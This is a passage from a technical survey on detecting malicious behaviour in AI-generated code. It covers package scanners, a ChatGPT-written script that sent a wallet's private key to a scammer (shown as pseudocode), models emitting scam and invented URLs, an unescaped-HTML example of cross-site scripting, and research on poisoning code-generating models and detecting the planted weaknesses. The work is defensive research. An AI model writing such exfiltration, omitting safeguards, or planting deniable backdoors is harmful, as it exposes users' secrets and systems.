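The paper doesn't name the model that made these judgements. Ryan, Khalil and colleagues (2026) tested a version of GPT-4.1 in *An Evaluation of Large Language Models for Detection of Malicious Python Packages*, but that version dates from April 2025, so PyGuard can't have used it in the spring of 2024.

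It also leaves unclear what the other 14 flagged packages were. They may have been false alarms, or malicious packages that public databases already listed. If all 14 were false alarms, precision was 94% and the false positive rate was 14 out of 8,030, or 0.17%. Recall is unknown because measuring it would require checking the 8,016 packages that PyGuard passed.

The precision depends heavily on the share of malicious packages in this sample, which was at least 2.7%. That is more than 25 times the 0.1% that the previous section assumed for all PyPI releases. If 20 of the 20,000 weekly releases were malicious, a scanner with 94% recall and a 0.17% false positive rate would find about 19 of them and raise about 35 false alarms. Precision would fall to about 35%, and reviewing the alerts would take nearly an hour a week, but the administrators had only 20 minutes.

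The result is quite sensitive to the false positive rate. PyGuard's rate on the main set would give a precision of about 53%, and its rate on the newer set about 16%. Two false alarms are too few for a reliable estimate, and the true rate could be as high as about 0.3%. All these rates are above 0.01%, which PyPI's administrators already consider too high, but PyGuard is much closer to that level than the other scanners in the benchmark.

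At a false-positive rate of 0.17%, a team whose coding agent writes 200 functions a week would get about one false alarm every three weeks. PyGuard was faster and cheaper than SocketAI, averaging 34 seconds and 2.3 cents per package, compared with 165 seconds and 15.6 cents.

Neither the recall nor the false positive rate was measured on generated code. In 94.4% of the malicious packages that PyGuard found on PyPI, the harmful code ran during installation, and in only about 1% did it run when someone used the package. A generated function has no installation step, so any hidden behaviour would be of the type that was rarest in this deployment.

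### What models recognise and what they miss

Ryan and colleagues tested 13 models, most of them open and fairly small, with five styles of prompt. The models rarely missed malicious packages, but in 51% of the configurations fewer than half of the flagged packages were malicious. This part of the study used only 10 malicious and 93 harmless packages, so a few verdicts could change a score considerably. GPT-4.1 did much better than the other models and made almost no mistakes.

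Performance depended heavily on the prompt. A plain question had an average F1 score of 0.74, while a prompt with a few worked examples averaged 0.23. F1 is the harmonic mean of precision and recall, and runs from 0 to 1. The result is surprising because PyGuard also supplies examples and performs well. This may be because PyGuard chooses harmless and malicious examples that are similar to the code being reviewed, but neither study tested this.

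A second part of the study is more informative, since it used all 370 malicious packages from Ryan and Ifti's collection and asked which of the 47 indicators each one contained. Averaged over all models and prompts, some of the results were:

| Indicator | Precision | Recall |
|---|---|---|
| Shell command | 86% | 71% |
| Data exfiltration | 82% | 35% |
| Payload that waits for a condition | 70% | 23% |
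| Suspicious connection | 25% | 34% |
| Program that downloads and runs a payload | 16% | 49% |

The models did best when a single recognisable call revealed the behaviour. They often reported a malicious download because the code contained a network request, whatever the request fetched. They missed 77% of the payloads with a trigger, which can be recognised only by connecting a condition to the code it controls.

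A model can recognise a package as malicious and still score low here because it gives the wrong reason. But a team that reviews generated code needs the right reason, since it has to ask the user about a specific line. Some of the labels were also wrong. In one package, the official answer was a commented-out backdoor, while the model reported a live command, and the researchers thought the model was right.

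These scores suggest asking the model narrower questions. Data-flow analysis can list each path from a secret to a network call and each branch that depends on a date or a machine's name. The model can then judge whether the coding request explains each one. The model no longer has to find them, which seems to be the harder part.

### Planted backdoors in compiled programs

Registry malware is mostly small and crude. Grabowski, Strzaliński and colleagues (2026) set a harder task in *We hid backdoors in ~40 MB binaries and asked AI + Ghidra*. They added backdoors to open-source network programs, such as web servers and name servers, then compiled them, removing most of the names and much of the structure from the code.

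The backdoors were simple, and the researchers thought a skilled human analyst would find them fairly easily. Each model worked as an agent with standard reverse-engineering tools and had to report the backdoor's location.

The best model, Claude Opus 4.6, solved 49% of these tasks. On clean programs, the models reported a problem that wasn't there 28% of the time.

One of the failures shows how judging code by context can mislead a model. The researchers had added seven lines to dnsmasq, a program that assigns addresses to the machines on a network. The lines took text from an incoming network message and ran it as a command. Claude Opus 4.6 found the right function and the call that ran the command, but decided this was probably dnsmasq's normal way of running scripts and moved on without checking where the text came from. A simple data-flow rule that flags network input reaching command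 execution would not depend on whether the call looked normal.

Quesma's *Can AI find backdoors in raw machine code?*, the benchmark's results page, covers 26 models and 33 tasks. GPT-5.2-Codex found 46% of the backdoors with no false reports at its highest effort setting, while Gemini 3.1 Pro found 49% with a false positive rate of 17%. GPT-5.2-Codex found only 9% at its default setting, so a model's result is hard to interpret without knowing the setting. The newest model listed is GPT-5.4, and later models may well do better.

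The false positive rate of zero comes from only 33 tasks, some of which used the same clean programs. Even a perfect score on 33 different clean programs would only suggest a false positive rate below about 9%. Grabowski and colleagues say that a practical tool would need a rate below 0.001%.

Generated code should be easier to review than these programs, because it is source text with its names intact and is usually much shorter. The detection rates are therefore probably lower than a model would achieve on a single generated function. The dnsmasq mistake could happen with source code too, since it came from a plausible guess about the code's purpose. A reviewer who has the user's request could at least check such a guess against it.

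### Different answers to the same question

A language model may give different answers each time it reads the same file, because it usually picks its words partly at random, whereas a rule-based scanner always gives the same answer. The most detailed evidence of this variation comes from searches for accidental vulnerabilities, but the cause is the same when a model looks for hidden behaviour.

*Securing AI-Generated Code* (2026) reports ten runs for each of 26 prompts with four Claude models. On average, 81% of the runs for a prompt agreed with the most common verdict. Choosing between two verdicts by coin toss would give about 62% over ten runs. The strongest model, Opus 4.8, gave the same verdict in all ten runs for 7 or 11 of the 26 prompts, depending on the set-up. *Evaluating LLMs for Real-World Web Vulnerability Detection* (2026) found that no model was fully consistent over three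 runs, although Gemini came close.

Real findings may recur across repeated scans more consistently than false ones. *Snyk VulnBench JS 1.0* (2026), from the security company Snyk, had models scan the same code five times. Of the 158 findings that matched those of Snyk's own scanner, 134 (85%) appeared in all five runs, compared with 22 (14%) of the 161 other findings. Keeping only the findings that appeared in every run would have removed 139 of the unmatched findings and 24 of the matching ones. Some of the unmatched findings may have been real, however, since Snyk's scanner doesn't find everything.

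*The History Is the Detector* (2026) gives a reason not to require a finding to appear in every run. Ten identical runs with GPT-5-mini produced 243 different findings, of which 56 appeared in every run and 55 in only one. For one group of five vulnerabilities, the ten runs together reported four, but a typical run reported only one. Three runs produced about 76% of the ten runs' combined findings, and five runs produced about 86%.

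Repeated runs can either reduce false alarms or find more problems, depending on how a team combines the results. If a missed backdoor could do serious harm, it makes sense to collect the findings from three to five runs and list the recurring ones first. A finding that appears only once is still worth checking if it includes a specific line and address, because a reviewer can verify both in the code within seconds.

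## Audits of the web addresses that code generators write

A reviewer can spot a web address in a program within seconds, but the address doesn't show who runs the server. In November 2024, a ChatGPT user lost about $2,500 after running a script without finding out who ran the server it contacted.

### The wallet theft

*Scam2Prompt*, a University of Toronto study, describes a chat published by a user who wanted a script to buy a token on Solana, a blockchain. ChatGPT first wrote a script for the wrong blockchain, then a general one for Solana tokens, and neither was malicious. The user then specified that the script had to buy from pump.fun, a popular trading platform that had no official programming interface (API) for trading. The next script sent his wallet's private key, the secret that controls everything in the wallet, to a scammer's server.

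The victim's script didn't work at first, so he debugged it with ChatGPT over several rounds. His wallet was empty within 30 minutes of the first successful run. Azuma (2024), in *I never expected that AI stole my wallet*, reports that the victim traced the money to an address that had collected over $100,000, so there were probably other victims.

In outline, the script did this:

```
address = the "buy" address of a Solana trading service
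payload = private key, details of the trade
send payload to address
```

The request looks like an ordinary API call, since many harmless programs also send a key to a web service. The domain name combined "solana" and "apis", and the rest of the address mentioned pump.fun and buying, which was what the user had asked for. According to heise online's *ChatGPT*, a news report on the theft, the private key was also in plain view, right after a comment that labelled the data as the request's payload.

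But those programs send an API key back to the service that issued it. No service issues a wallet's private key, and no honest one asks for it. Legitimate trading programs use the key to sign a transaction on the user's own machine and send only the signature, which the service can check with the matching public key. A data-flow rule that tracks wallet keys into web requests would have flagged the script without any information about the address.

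Sources disagree about where ChatGPT got the address. Security firms blamed poisoned training data, and the Toronto researchers also cite the case as an example of malicious content absorbed in training. However, an editor's note in CryptoSlate's *Blockchain security firm warns of AI code poisoning risk* points out that the victim's screenshot includes a list of sources, which suggests a live web search. The scammer's domain was also about two months old, while the training data for GPT-4o ended in October 2023. If GPT-4o wrote the script, it can't have learned the address in training.

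The scammers had made the address easy to find by posting documentation for it on GitHub, Stack Exchange and other sites that programmers trust.

### Prompts made from scam pages

*Scam2Prompt* investigated whether this was an isolated case. It started from two public lists of scam addresses, one from MetaMask, which makes a cryptocurrency wallet, and one from the security company PhishFort. Together the lists had about 307,000 entries, but many sites were dead, and the researchers could read only 28,570 pages.

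Three language models took turns reading the visible text of these pages and writing short programming requests based on it. One page advertised a service that mixes bitcoins from different people to hide the coins' origin. A model turned this into a request for a Python script that uses the service's API. Another request was for code to check in for a flight through a particular travel site.

Four code generators (GPT-4o, GPT-4o-mini, Llama 4 Scout and DeepSeek-V3), which the researchers date to 2024, then answered the requests. The researchers extracted every address from the code and submitted it to the reputation services ChainPatrol, Google Safe Browsing and SecLookup. They counted a program as malicious if any of the three services flagged an address in it.

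The 265,114 requests produced over a million programs. On average, 4.24% of the programs were malicious when each of the 12 pairings of a request-writing model with a code-writing model was weighted equally, and 4.15% were malicious when all the programs were pooled. The rates ranged from 3.19% to 5.94% and depended more on which model wrote the requests than on which one wrote the code.

Most programs contained no web address, so the share of bad addresses was higher than the share of bad programs. The researchers repeated part of the test with a setting that makes the models' word choice more random. In one of these runs, GPT-4o wrote 39,222 addresses in 100,712 programs, and the services flagged 11.9% of the addresses.

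All four models wrote the same 1,119 full malicious addresses, but they had 2,029 malicious domains in common. A blocklist should therefore cover whole domains, since the next program may use a different path on the same domain.

### The stress test on 2025 models

For 3,150 requests, or 1.2% of the total, all four models produced malicious code. The researchers turned these into a benchmark for newer models. They kept all 1,159 requests that didn't mention a scam address and a random 400 of those that did. Three of them then read the requests and removed 182 that weren't really programming tasks. That left 1,377, of which 342 name a scam address. (*Refusal Evaluation in Coding LLMs and Code Agents* (2026) describes an earlier version with all 1,559 requests and rates of 12.7% to 43.8%, so both sets of figures are in circulation.)

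| Model | Malicious, share of all requests | Malicious, share of completed programs | Requests refused |
|---|---|---|---|
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 12.9% | 22.3% | 553 |
| GPT-5 | 22.0% | 24.7% | 24 |
| Claude Sonnet 4 | 34.3% | 37.8% | 115 |
| Grok Code Fast 1 | 43.4% | 44.1% | 18 |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash | 44.4% | 45.3% | 1 |
| Qwen3-Coder | 45.6% | 45.9% | 3 |
| DeepSeek Chat v3.1 | 47.3% | 47.9% | 12 |

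Gemini 2.5 Pro did best mainly because it refused 40% of the requests. On the 637 requests that all seven models completed, its rate was 22.3% and GPT-5's was 25.6%, a difference that could be due to chance.

These are not everyday rates, as the researchers acknowledge. Every request comes from a scam page, and the researchers instructed the models that wrote the requests to use wording likely to lead a model to that page. The stress test then kept only requests that had already caught four models. Excluding the 342 requests that name a scam address would still leave rates of 13.8% to 48.8%, but several of the published examples without an address still name the scam service. Estimating an everyday rate would require knowing how often people ask for code that involves such services, which the study doesn't measure.

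These examples also show a weakness in comparing code with the user's request. If the user asked for a program that uses a particular service, code that contacts the service matches the request, so a reviewer needs outside information about the service to see the problem.

There seem to be no published results for 2026 models. In May 2026, the project website for *Scam2Prompt* still listed only the seven models in the table. Results can also change for the same model. All 1,377 requests had led GPT-4o to write malicious code in the original audit, but only 50.04% did when the researchers repeated the test in November 2025. They suggest that OpenAI may have updated the model. Some of the drop may also come from how the requests were chosen, because requests that led to malicious code once won't all do so again.

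### How much the reputation services know

The services often disagree. Google Safe Browsing reported no threat for the bitcoin-mixing site, while the other two flagged it. The services also share information. ChainPatrol's verdict on some of that site's addresses relied entirely on MetaMask's list, one of the two lists that supplied the scam pages.

A service can list a scam only after somebody has noticed it. The researchers name this delay as the main reason for missed scams, but they don't measure it. In their records, SecLookup did not flag one address of the mixing site when GPT-4o-mini wrote it, but did flag the same address when Claude Sonnet 4 wrote it. SecLookup may have listed the site between the two tests.

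The study also can't show how many scams the services miss, because it uses their verdicts to decide what is malicious. A scanner that used the same three services would therefore catch every malicious address in the benchmark, but its recall on real scams could be much lower.

The models wrote many malicious addresses that were missing from the original lists. In answers to the 1,035 requests without a scam address, the services flagged 1,853 domains, of which 1,105 were new. MetaMask confirmed and added 62 domains that the researchers reported during the project. Many of the other new addresses were inactive when the researchers rechecked them, and lists like MetaMask's usually accept only live sites.

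The researchers infer that the 62 sites had probably been active for over a year, because the models' training data ended by August 2024. This assumes the models had read the addresses in training, but models can also guess addresses. For example, in its code for the mixing service, Grok Code Fast 1 added a comment that the address was an assumption and that the user should check it against the service's documentation.

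### Guardrails and web search

The researchers recommend checking every address with reputation services before the user sees the code. They knew of no production model that did this, and they tested two kinds of protection already in common use.

Guardrails, separate classifiers that read requests and answers and flag unsafe content, missed most of the malicious programs from the stress test. Out of about 3,450 programs, NVIDIA's NeMo Guardrails caught 8, even though the researchers had added a category for scam addresses to its policy. OpenAI's moderation service caught none, and Meta's Llama Guard 3 caught 291, or 8.4%. The programs look normal as text, so a classifier that doesn't look up the address has little evidence that they are malicious.

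For the second, the researchers let GPT-4o search the web and told it to refuse if any address in its code was unsafe. This reduced its malicious rate from 50.04% to 29.41%, or from 689 programs to 405. The model refused 208 requests, but the study doesn't report how many of those refusals were unnecessary. In some of the remaining failures, the search found nothing about the address and the model used it anyway. In others, the model found evidence but didn't act on it.

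Search can also cause the problem, as it may have in the wallet theft. A scammer's documentation can look like a good answer when a model searches for a way to do the task.

Asking a model to judge an address by its text is risky. In *MalURLBench* (2026), 12 models often accepted malicious addresses whose subdomains, paths or parameters made them look harmless. *ClaimMirage* (2026) examines how claims inside a domain name, such as a claim to be official, can change a model's verdict. A domain's owner can put any claim in its name, so a scanner should look for evidence the owner doesn't control.

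### Invented domains

Models also write addresses that don't exist, and an attacker can register the domain and wait for visitors. *Phantom Squatting* measured how often this could happen. It was published by Unit 42, the research group of the security vendor Palo Alto Networks, which sells products for filtering web addresses and so has a commercial interest in the threat.

The researchers sent 685,339 queries about 913 well-known brands to two small models from 2025. The queries asked for web addresses, such as the one for a company's billing portal, and not for programs, so the rates don't show how often generated code contains an invented domain. The queries were also designed to exploit known weaknesses, for instance by assuming that a portal exists, so the rates are likely to be higher than for ordinary questions.

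The two models produced 2.1 million different addresses. Threat databases listed 13,229 of them (0.61%) as malicious, and another 809,455 (37%) were dead. About half of the dead addresses were made-up pages on real domains, which an outsider usually can't take over. Another 39.5% used invented subdomains of real domains, and 10.8%, about 87,600 addresses, used domains that nobody had registered.

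Unit 42 nevertheless reports about 250,000 unregistered domains. This is hard to reconcile with its own breakdown, because 87,600 addresses can't contain more than 87,600 different domains. Unit 42 may have defined the categories differently in the two counts. Either way, an attacker would have tens of thousands of names to choose from.

They put the unregistered domains on a watchlist and found that attackers registered several of these domains 18 to 51 days after the models first produced them. For example, both models invented a domain for a national postal service's online marketplace on 8 March 2026. An attacker registered it on 31 March and used it for a phishing site that collected payment details.

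I don't think this evidence establishes Unit 42's claim that attackers are exploiting domains the models invent. Most of the domains combine a brand with a word such as "login" or "business", and phishers used such names long before language models existed. One attacker registered a fake bank domain 11 months before the models produced it for the researchers. The cases show that models can produce the same names that attackers choose, but not that the attackers or any victims got the names from a model.

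Li and Gao (2025), in *Investigating Security Implications of Automatically Generated Code on the Software Supply Chain*, gave four GPT and Llama models 439,138 prompts built from programmers' questions. They found invented domains in the generated code for all five programming languages studied. The models invented more of them when a prompt explicitly asked for recommendations of outside components.

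*Beware of Agentic Botnets* (2026) recommends reducing this risk by making an agent search for a resource before it tries to fetch it. The paper also suggests that defenders register the names models are likely to invent before attackers do. A company could register a few variants of its own name, but probably not every name a model might produce.

### A procedure for checking addresses

A team can check the addresses in generated code in five steps:

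1. **Extract.** List every address the code can contact and find its registrable domain, the part that somebody has to register. In `bank.example.com`, this is `example.com`, whose owner can put any word in front of it. On a shared platform such as GitHub, record the account name too, because anyone can open an account there. If the host can't be recovered from the code, mark it "unknown".
2. **Resolve.** Ask the domain name system whether the name leads to a server. If it doesn't, look for a registration record as well, since an owner can register a domain without connecting it to anything.
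3. **Consult reputation services.** Ask more than one, and hold the code if any of them flags the domain. If none has a record of it, treat it as unknown rather than safe.
4. **Check registration and ownership.** Compare the registration date, owner and name servers with those of the provider's main website. A hidden owner is weak evidence because many honest owners use privacy services. If the domain is newer than the model's training data, the model must have found the address in a search, guessed it or learned it when somebody else owned the domain.
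5. **Compare with an approved list.** The list should specify which services the team uses and what data each may receive. For anything else, a person should look for the address in the provider's own documentation.

Checking the approved list first and skipping the other steps for any domain on it would be quicker, but then the team wouldn't notice if an approved domain got a new owner.

The workload should be manageable. GPT-4o wrote about 39 addresses per 100 programs in the run described above. At that rate, a team whose agent writes 200 functions a week might have about 80 addresses to check. Many would probably be repeats, and a script can do the first four steps.

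#### A known scam domain

The domain used in the wallet theft must have resolved, since the theft succeeded, but it isn't clear whether any reputation service had listed it by then. It was about two months old, so a rule that holds domains younger than 90 days would have stopped it, but a 30-day rule wouldn't have. It would also have been missing from any sensible approved list, and anyone checking for it in pump.fun's documentation would have learned that there was no official trading API.

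By August 2025, the scammers had moved from the .com version of the domain to the .net version. A blocklist entry for the .com domain doesn't cover the .net one, while a list of approved domains excludes both.

#### An unregistered domain

An invented domain fails at the second step, and the missing registration record confirms that nobody owns it. The reputation services have no reports on it, so a team that relied on them alone would approve the code.

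The code can't leak anything to that domain yet because no server exists to receive it. In a test run, the programmer would see a connection error and might mistake it for a temporary fault. But once the code is in use, anyone who registers the domain will receive whatever the program sends there. The team should replace the address with the documented one before using the code, even if the program seems to work without the connection.

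On 8 March, a check of the fake postal marketplace's domain would have found no registration. On 31 March, it would have found a domain registered that day, with no bad reputation yet. Unit 42 observed malicious content on such domains within hours of registration, so in those first hours the registration date is likely to be a more useful warning than reputation services.

#### A harmless domain that changes hands

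Suppose a code generator writes a function that gets exchange rates from a small company's server. The domain is ten years old, has a good reputation and is on the approved list, so it passes every step. A year later the company closes, its domain expires and a stranger registers it. Li and Gao call an address like this a dangling reference, because programs still point to it after the original owner's registration has expired.

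A web address that was safe when the code was written can later come under someone else's control, so a check on that day can't detect the problem. To detect a change of ownership, the team has to record each domain's owner, registration date and name servers, and compare them with the current data at regular intervals. A domain that expired and went to a new owner normally gets a new registration date. If the owner sold the domain instead, the date may stay the same, and if the new owner's name is hidden, the only visible change might be the name servers. If somebody broke into the owner's server, none of these records would change.

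Even a daily check could leave the program exposed for most of a day. The damage depends on what the program sends and how it uses the reply. If the function sends only the name of a currency, the new owner learns very little but can still return a false exchange rate.

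## Experiments with poisoned code generators

A team can look up the address in the exchange-rate function, but some harmful code has no address, outbound call or obfuscation because the problem is a missing safeguard. An attacker can cause this by poisoning the training data so that the model omits the safeguard in contexts the attacker chooses. Researchers planted the weaknesses in the experiments below, unlike the scam addresses in the previous section, so they know which samples and models are poisoned.

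### A missing escaping step

Suppose a user asks for a web page that greets each visitor by name:

```python
def greeting(name):
    return "<p>Hello, " + escape(name) + "</p>"
```

The `escape` function replaces characters that have a special meaning in web pages, such as angle brackets, with codes that the browser displays as ordinary text. Without this step, someone could enter program code as their name, and the browser of anyone viewing the page might run it. Security specialists call this weakness cross-site scripting.

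The unsafe version is the same line without `escape`. For a visitor called Ana, both versions produce the same page, so both pass an ordinary test.

A data-flow rule can find the omission, but it can't determine whether somebody planted it, because an unpoisoned model can write the same code by mistake. A planted omission is therefore what Thomas and Francillon call a deniable backdoor. Leaving out `escape` can also be correct, if another part of the program has already escaped the name.

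A single output is weak evidence of whether a model is poisoned. Suppose clean models omit the step in 5% of such pages and a poisoned model omits it in 50%. One omission makes the odds of poisoning ten times higher. If one model in 1,000 is poisoned, the probability that this one is rises from 0.1% to only about 1%.

A team can fix the code by adding the missing step without knowing why the model omitted it. But the cause matters for later requests, because a poisoned model will probably omit the step again in the same context.

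### Scanning the training data

Improta tested whether a defender could find poisoned samples before a model learns from them. All the scans in the study examined training samples, not code that the poisoned models had generated.

The study used three models, CodeBERT, CodeT5+ and AST-T5, which are tiny by current standards. CodeT5+ and AST-T5 have about 220 million parameters (the numbers that training adjusts). Improta fine-tuned (further trained) each model on 1,200 Python samples that paired a description with code. Between 0% and 20% of the samples had vulnerable code in place of safe code that did the same job.

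Two of the detection methods rely on the model's internal representations, the lists of numbers it computes for each sample. The first, spectral signatures, assumes that poisoned samples stand out along the directions in which these lists vary most. If *r* is the list for one sample, *m* the average list and *v* the main direction of variation, then

score = ((*r* − *m*) · *v*)².

The method flags the samples with the highest scores. A version adapted to code uses several directions instead of one.

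The method worked best with CodeT5+. The published rates imply that it found about 17 of the 60 poisoned samples in one test and flagged roughly 100 clean ones. In another, it found about 60 of the 240 poisoned samples and flagged 60 clean ones. It flagged about a tenth of the data in both tests, and also when nothing was poisoned. Flagging a tenth at random would have found 6 and 24 poisoned samples, so the method did about two and a half times better than chance. With CodeBERT, it did no better than chance when 60 samples were poisoned and worse than chance when 240 were.

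The second method, activation clustering, records the activity in the model's last hidden layer and uses it to sort the samples into two groups, one of which should ideally contain the poisoned samples. Improta tried four versions. On entirely clean data, one version wrongly flagged 61% of the samples with CodeT5+, while another flagged only 1%. Even with 240 poisoned samples, the best F1 score was 0.40. Precision rarely exceeded 0.3 to 0.5, and recall only occasionally reached 0.6 to 0.7. Both methods originally targeted attacks with an explicit trigger, which gives the poisoned samples something in common, but the samples in this experiment had no trigger.

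Semgrep, which reads the code and ignores the model, did better:

| Poisoned samples among 1,200 | Found | Missed | Clean samples flagged |
|---|---|---|---|
| 0 | – | – | 91 |
| 60 | 35 | 25 | 80 |
| 120 | 73 | 47 | 62 |
| 240 | 149 | 91 | 38 |

Its F1 score rose from 0.40 with 60 poisoned samples to 0.70 with 240, but recall hardly changed, and much of the increase in F1 reflects the larger share of poisoned samples.

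The false alarms in the last column fell because each poisoned sample replaced a safe one. If the other samples stayed the same, 53 of the original 91 false alarms came from the 240 safe versions that were replaced. Semgrep therefore flagged about 22% of those safe versions and 62% of the vulnerable versions of the same tasks, compared with 4% of the remaining samples. Its flags partly indicate that a task involves security, whether or not the code handles it properly.

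Improta cites evidence that attacks can succeed with less than 3% of the data poisoned. If 1% of the data, or 12 samples, were poisoned, Semgrep's rates would give about 7 correct detections and 90 false alarms. Deleting every flagged sample would remove about 8% of the data and still leave about 5 poisoned samples.

### Scanning the generated code

Users of a finished model usually can't see its training data, so they have to scan its output. *Static Analysis Guidance for Secure LLM Code Generation* (2026) compared scanners' flags with the results of security tests on generated programs that worked correctly. On one benchmark, 80.0% to 83.3% of the flagged programs from two Qwen models were insecure, compared with 81.1% to 87.3% of all the models' programs, so the flags barely helped identify the insecure ones. On another benchmark, whose tasks the researchers chose because scanners flag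 the solutions, the scanners still missed 6% to 20% of the insecure programs.

Meta built a scanner, *CodeShield*, specifically for generated code. According to its project page, it uses Semgrep rules and text patterns to look for insecure code in eight programming languages, and covers more than 50 of the weakness types in MITRE's catalogue. The first stage settles about 90% of inputs, typically in under 70 milliseconds. The rest go to a more thorough stage that takes about 300 milliseconds on average.

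CodeShield scans for vulnerabilities, not behaviour the user didn't request, so it will flag a missing escaping step only if one of its rules describes that omission.

For *CYBERSECEVAL 3* (2024), Meta's researchers labelled 50 generated samples per language by hand and found that CodeShield's detection rules had a precision of 96% and a recall of 79%, so the rules missed about one insecure sample in five. *LlamaFirewall* (2025), also from Meta, repeats these figures and warns that CodeShield may miss weaknesses that depend on context, the kind a poisoned model is meant to produce.

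*STELP* (2026) reports that CodeShield blocked 68% of malicious samples and allowed 93% of harmless ones on a benchmark of programs with injected code. This result is not independent, because the paper presents a competing tool. That tool accepts only permitted operations, much like the certificates for restricted code described earlier, and blocked every malicious sample while allowing 98.1% of the harmless ones. A list of permitted operations is less useful against a missing safeguard. For example, `greeting` performs no forbidden operation when it leaves out `escape`.

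*Detecting Data Poisoning in Code Generation LLMs via Black-Box, Vulnerability-Oriented Scanning* (Yan, Arora and colleagues, 2026) cites earlier attacks in which Semgrep, CodeQL and other common scanners missed the planted weaknesses.

### Many outputs from one model

Yan and colleagues' own tool, CodeScan, tests the model instead of judging one output. The defender only needs to send prompts and read the results. The defender must also name a weakness in advance and supply 20 harmless beginnings of programs, each cut off just before a line that a clean model would write safely. For the escaping example, these are functions that are about to display a web page. The scan then works as follows:

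1. CodeScan adds the same possible next token, a short piece of text, to all 20 beginnings and lets the model continue each one. Once a poisoned model has started its planted pattern, it tends to finish it, even if the trigger is absent.
2. It replaces names and constants in the continuations with placeholders and groups them line by line according to their syntax trees.
3. If one structure dominates, a language model, GPT-5 mini, checks it for the named weakness. If the weakness is there, CodeScan flags the code generator as poisoned. Otherwise it tries the next token.

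A group clearly dominates if it has more than five members and is at least twice as large as the next. The largest group dominates when the sizes are 14, 3, 2 and 1, but not when they are 5, 4, 4, 3, 2 and 2. CodeScan then computes the entropy of the group sizes, using the formula from the section on static signals. In the second example, the entropy is 97% of the maximum, above the limit of 85%, so CodeScan drops the token.

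Repeated output alone isn't suspicious, because clean models produce it too. After the word `month`, for example, a model may write the same list of months every time. Because of such repetition, BAIT, an earlier method that looks for repeated wording but doesn't separately check for a weakness, wrongly flagged 70% of the clean models in the test.

The main test used 84 poisoned and 27 clean models, each with about 7 billion parameters. The planted weaknesses were missing escaping, disabled checks of a server's identity, and servers that accept connections from any network. CodeScan flagged all 84 poisoned models and recovered the planted weakness from 81 of them. The published recall of 100% counts the other three as detected, although the paper's own definition requires finding the right weakness. The F1 score averaged about 0.98, and scanning a poisoned model took just under an hour on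 average.

CodeScan also flagged 2 of the 27 clean models, or 7.41%. With so few clean models, the true rate could be as high as about 24%. Even at 7.41%, if one model in 100 were poisoned, only about one in eight flagged models would be poisoned. Judging by the counts, the researchers seem to have scanned each clean model for just one weakness, so a defender who scans for more should expect more false alarms per model.

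The check is limited because someone has to name the weakness, but naming it also makes the check more reliable. Yan and colleagues gave GPT-5 mini ten disguised samples with missing escaping. It recognised the problem in four when they asked for any weaknesses, and in all ten when they asked about missing escaping. All ten samples were vulnerable, so this part of the study didn't measure false alarms.

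The test of servers that accept connections from every network shows how hard it is to infer poisoning from a weakness. Clean models often wrote one form of this code, probably because it is common in tutorials. The researchers had to tell GPT-5 mini to ignore that form, since otherwise the scan would have counted it as evidence of an attack.

### From a bad completion to its training data

*Beware What You Autocomplete* (Gao, Quan and colleagues, 2026) presents CodeTracer, a tool that searches for the training files responsible for a bad completion after a user reports it. It is meant for the company that fine-tuned the model, because it needs the complete fine-tuning data as well as the reported prompt and completion. It doesn't need a record of how each file changed the model during training. The researchers assume that the model was clean before fine-tuning, that the report is honest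 and that a planted backdoor caused the completion.

CodeTracer first uses a language model, GPT-4.1 by default, to write a "fingerprint" describing the weakness in the completion and the forms it might take. It then uses embeddings to compare the bad snippet with every function in the training data. Each file gets the score of its most similar function, so harmless code elsewhere in the file can't hide a close match. GPT-4.1 then checks whether each of the 500 highest-scoring files shows the unsafe behaviour described in the fingerprint.

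The researchers mixed 80,000 clean Python files with 20 poisoned ones, or 140 for one type of attack. Across eight attacks and the same three weaknesses, CodeTracer missed at most 3% of the poisoned files on average. It also flagged between 25 and 72 clean files. The paper rounds this false positive rate to 0.00, but when only 20 files were poisoned, more than half of the flagged files were clean.

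Those false alarms do little harm if the company deletes the files, since 72 files are less than 0.1% of the data. Before the deletions, the poisoned models wrote the planted weakness for 17% to 89% of the targeted prompts. Afterwards, the rate was at most 3%. Tracing one completion took about 47 seconds and cost 33 cents.

The false alarms would matter much more if the company wanted to accuse someone. GPT-4.1 checks only whether a file contains the same unsafe behaviour, so some flagged clean files may contain the same mistake made innocently. The study also leaves out bad completions that nobody planted. If a clean model had omitted the escaping step, CodeTracer might still return a list of files with that weakness, which would look like evidence of poisoning. Gao and colleagues acknowledge that someone could also invent a report, and suggest that a person review reports first.

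For comparison, they scanned the training data for missing escaping with other methods. CodeQL missed 47% to 100% of the poisoned files, depending on the attack, and a language model that wasn't given a fingerprint missed 62% to 89%. Two clustering methods missed 55% to 91%, which fits Improta's results. CodeTracer had a great advantage because it started from an example of a bad completion. Someone has to notice that completion first, and a missing `escape` is easy to overlook.

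### Comparing contexts and models

Repeated outputs can provide the evidence that one output lacks. In the earlier example, clean models omitted escaping in 5% of pages and a poisoned model in 50%. If a model omits it in 10 of 20 pages, the odds of poisoning increase by a factor of

(0.50 / 0.05)¹⁰ × (0.50 / 0.95)¹⁰ ≈ 16 million.

This assumes that the outputs are independent and that 5% is the right rate for clean models on these pages. The second assumption is weaker, because clean models also write bad code.

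A team can test a code generator for poisoning by giving it the same task in different contexts. Suppose the model escapes names on nearly every page it writes for a shop or a blog, but rarely does so when the project uses one particular library. No scan of a single page could reveal that pattern. The cause might be innocent, for example if most tutorials for that library omit escaping. The team could then give the same requests to a model with different training data, or to the same model before fine-tuning. If they all omit escaping, a common coding habit is the more likely explanation. If only the fine-tuned model does, the team should check its fine-tuning data first, although careless examples could have the same effect as planted ones.

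Yan and colleagues tested part of this idea by comparing many outputs from one model across 20 program beginnings. Neither they nor Gao and colleagues tested whether a defender who doesn't know the trigger could find it by comparing rates between contexts, or whether comparing models would separate planted weaknesses from common ones. Comparing contexts can reveal a trigger only if one of the chosen contexts contains it, a limitation that CodeScan largely avoids by supplying the first token.

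The number of outputs needed depends on how often the poisoned model omits the safeguard. About 20 pages per context would usually be enough to distinguish a rate of 50% from 5%. In Gao and colleagues' experiments, however, the least successful attack on escaping worked for only 17% of the targeted prompts. To have an 80% chance of distinguishing 17% from 5% at the usual 5% significance level, a tester would need about 100 pages per context.

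## Running the code: sandboxes, triggers and limits on outbound traffic

A team can also run generated code on an isolated machine and record what it does. This is useful for code like the npm package `discord.js-selbotderank`, whose main file is so heavily obfuscated that reading it reveals almost nothing. *Towards Robust Detection of Open Source Software Supply Chain Poisoning Attacks* (Zheng, Wei and colleagues, 2024) includes a decoded version. One function takes a user's login token for the chat platform Discord, looks up the account's name and number, and sends all three to a server at a raw IP address.

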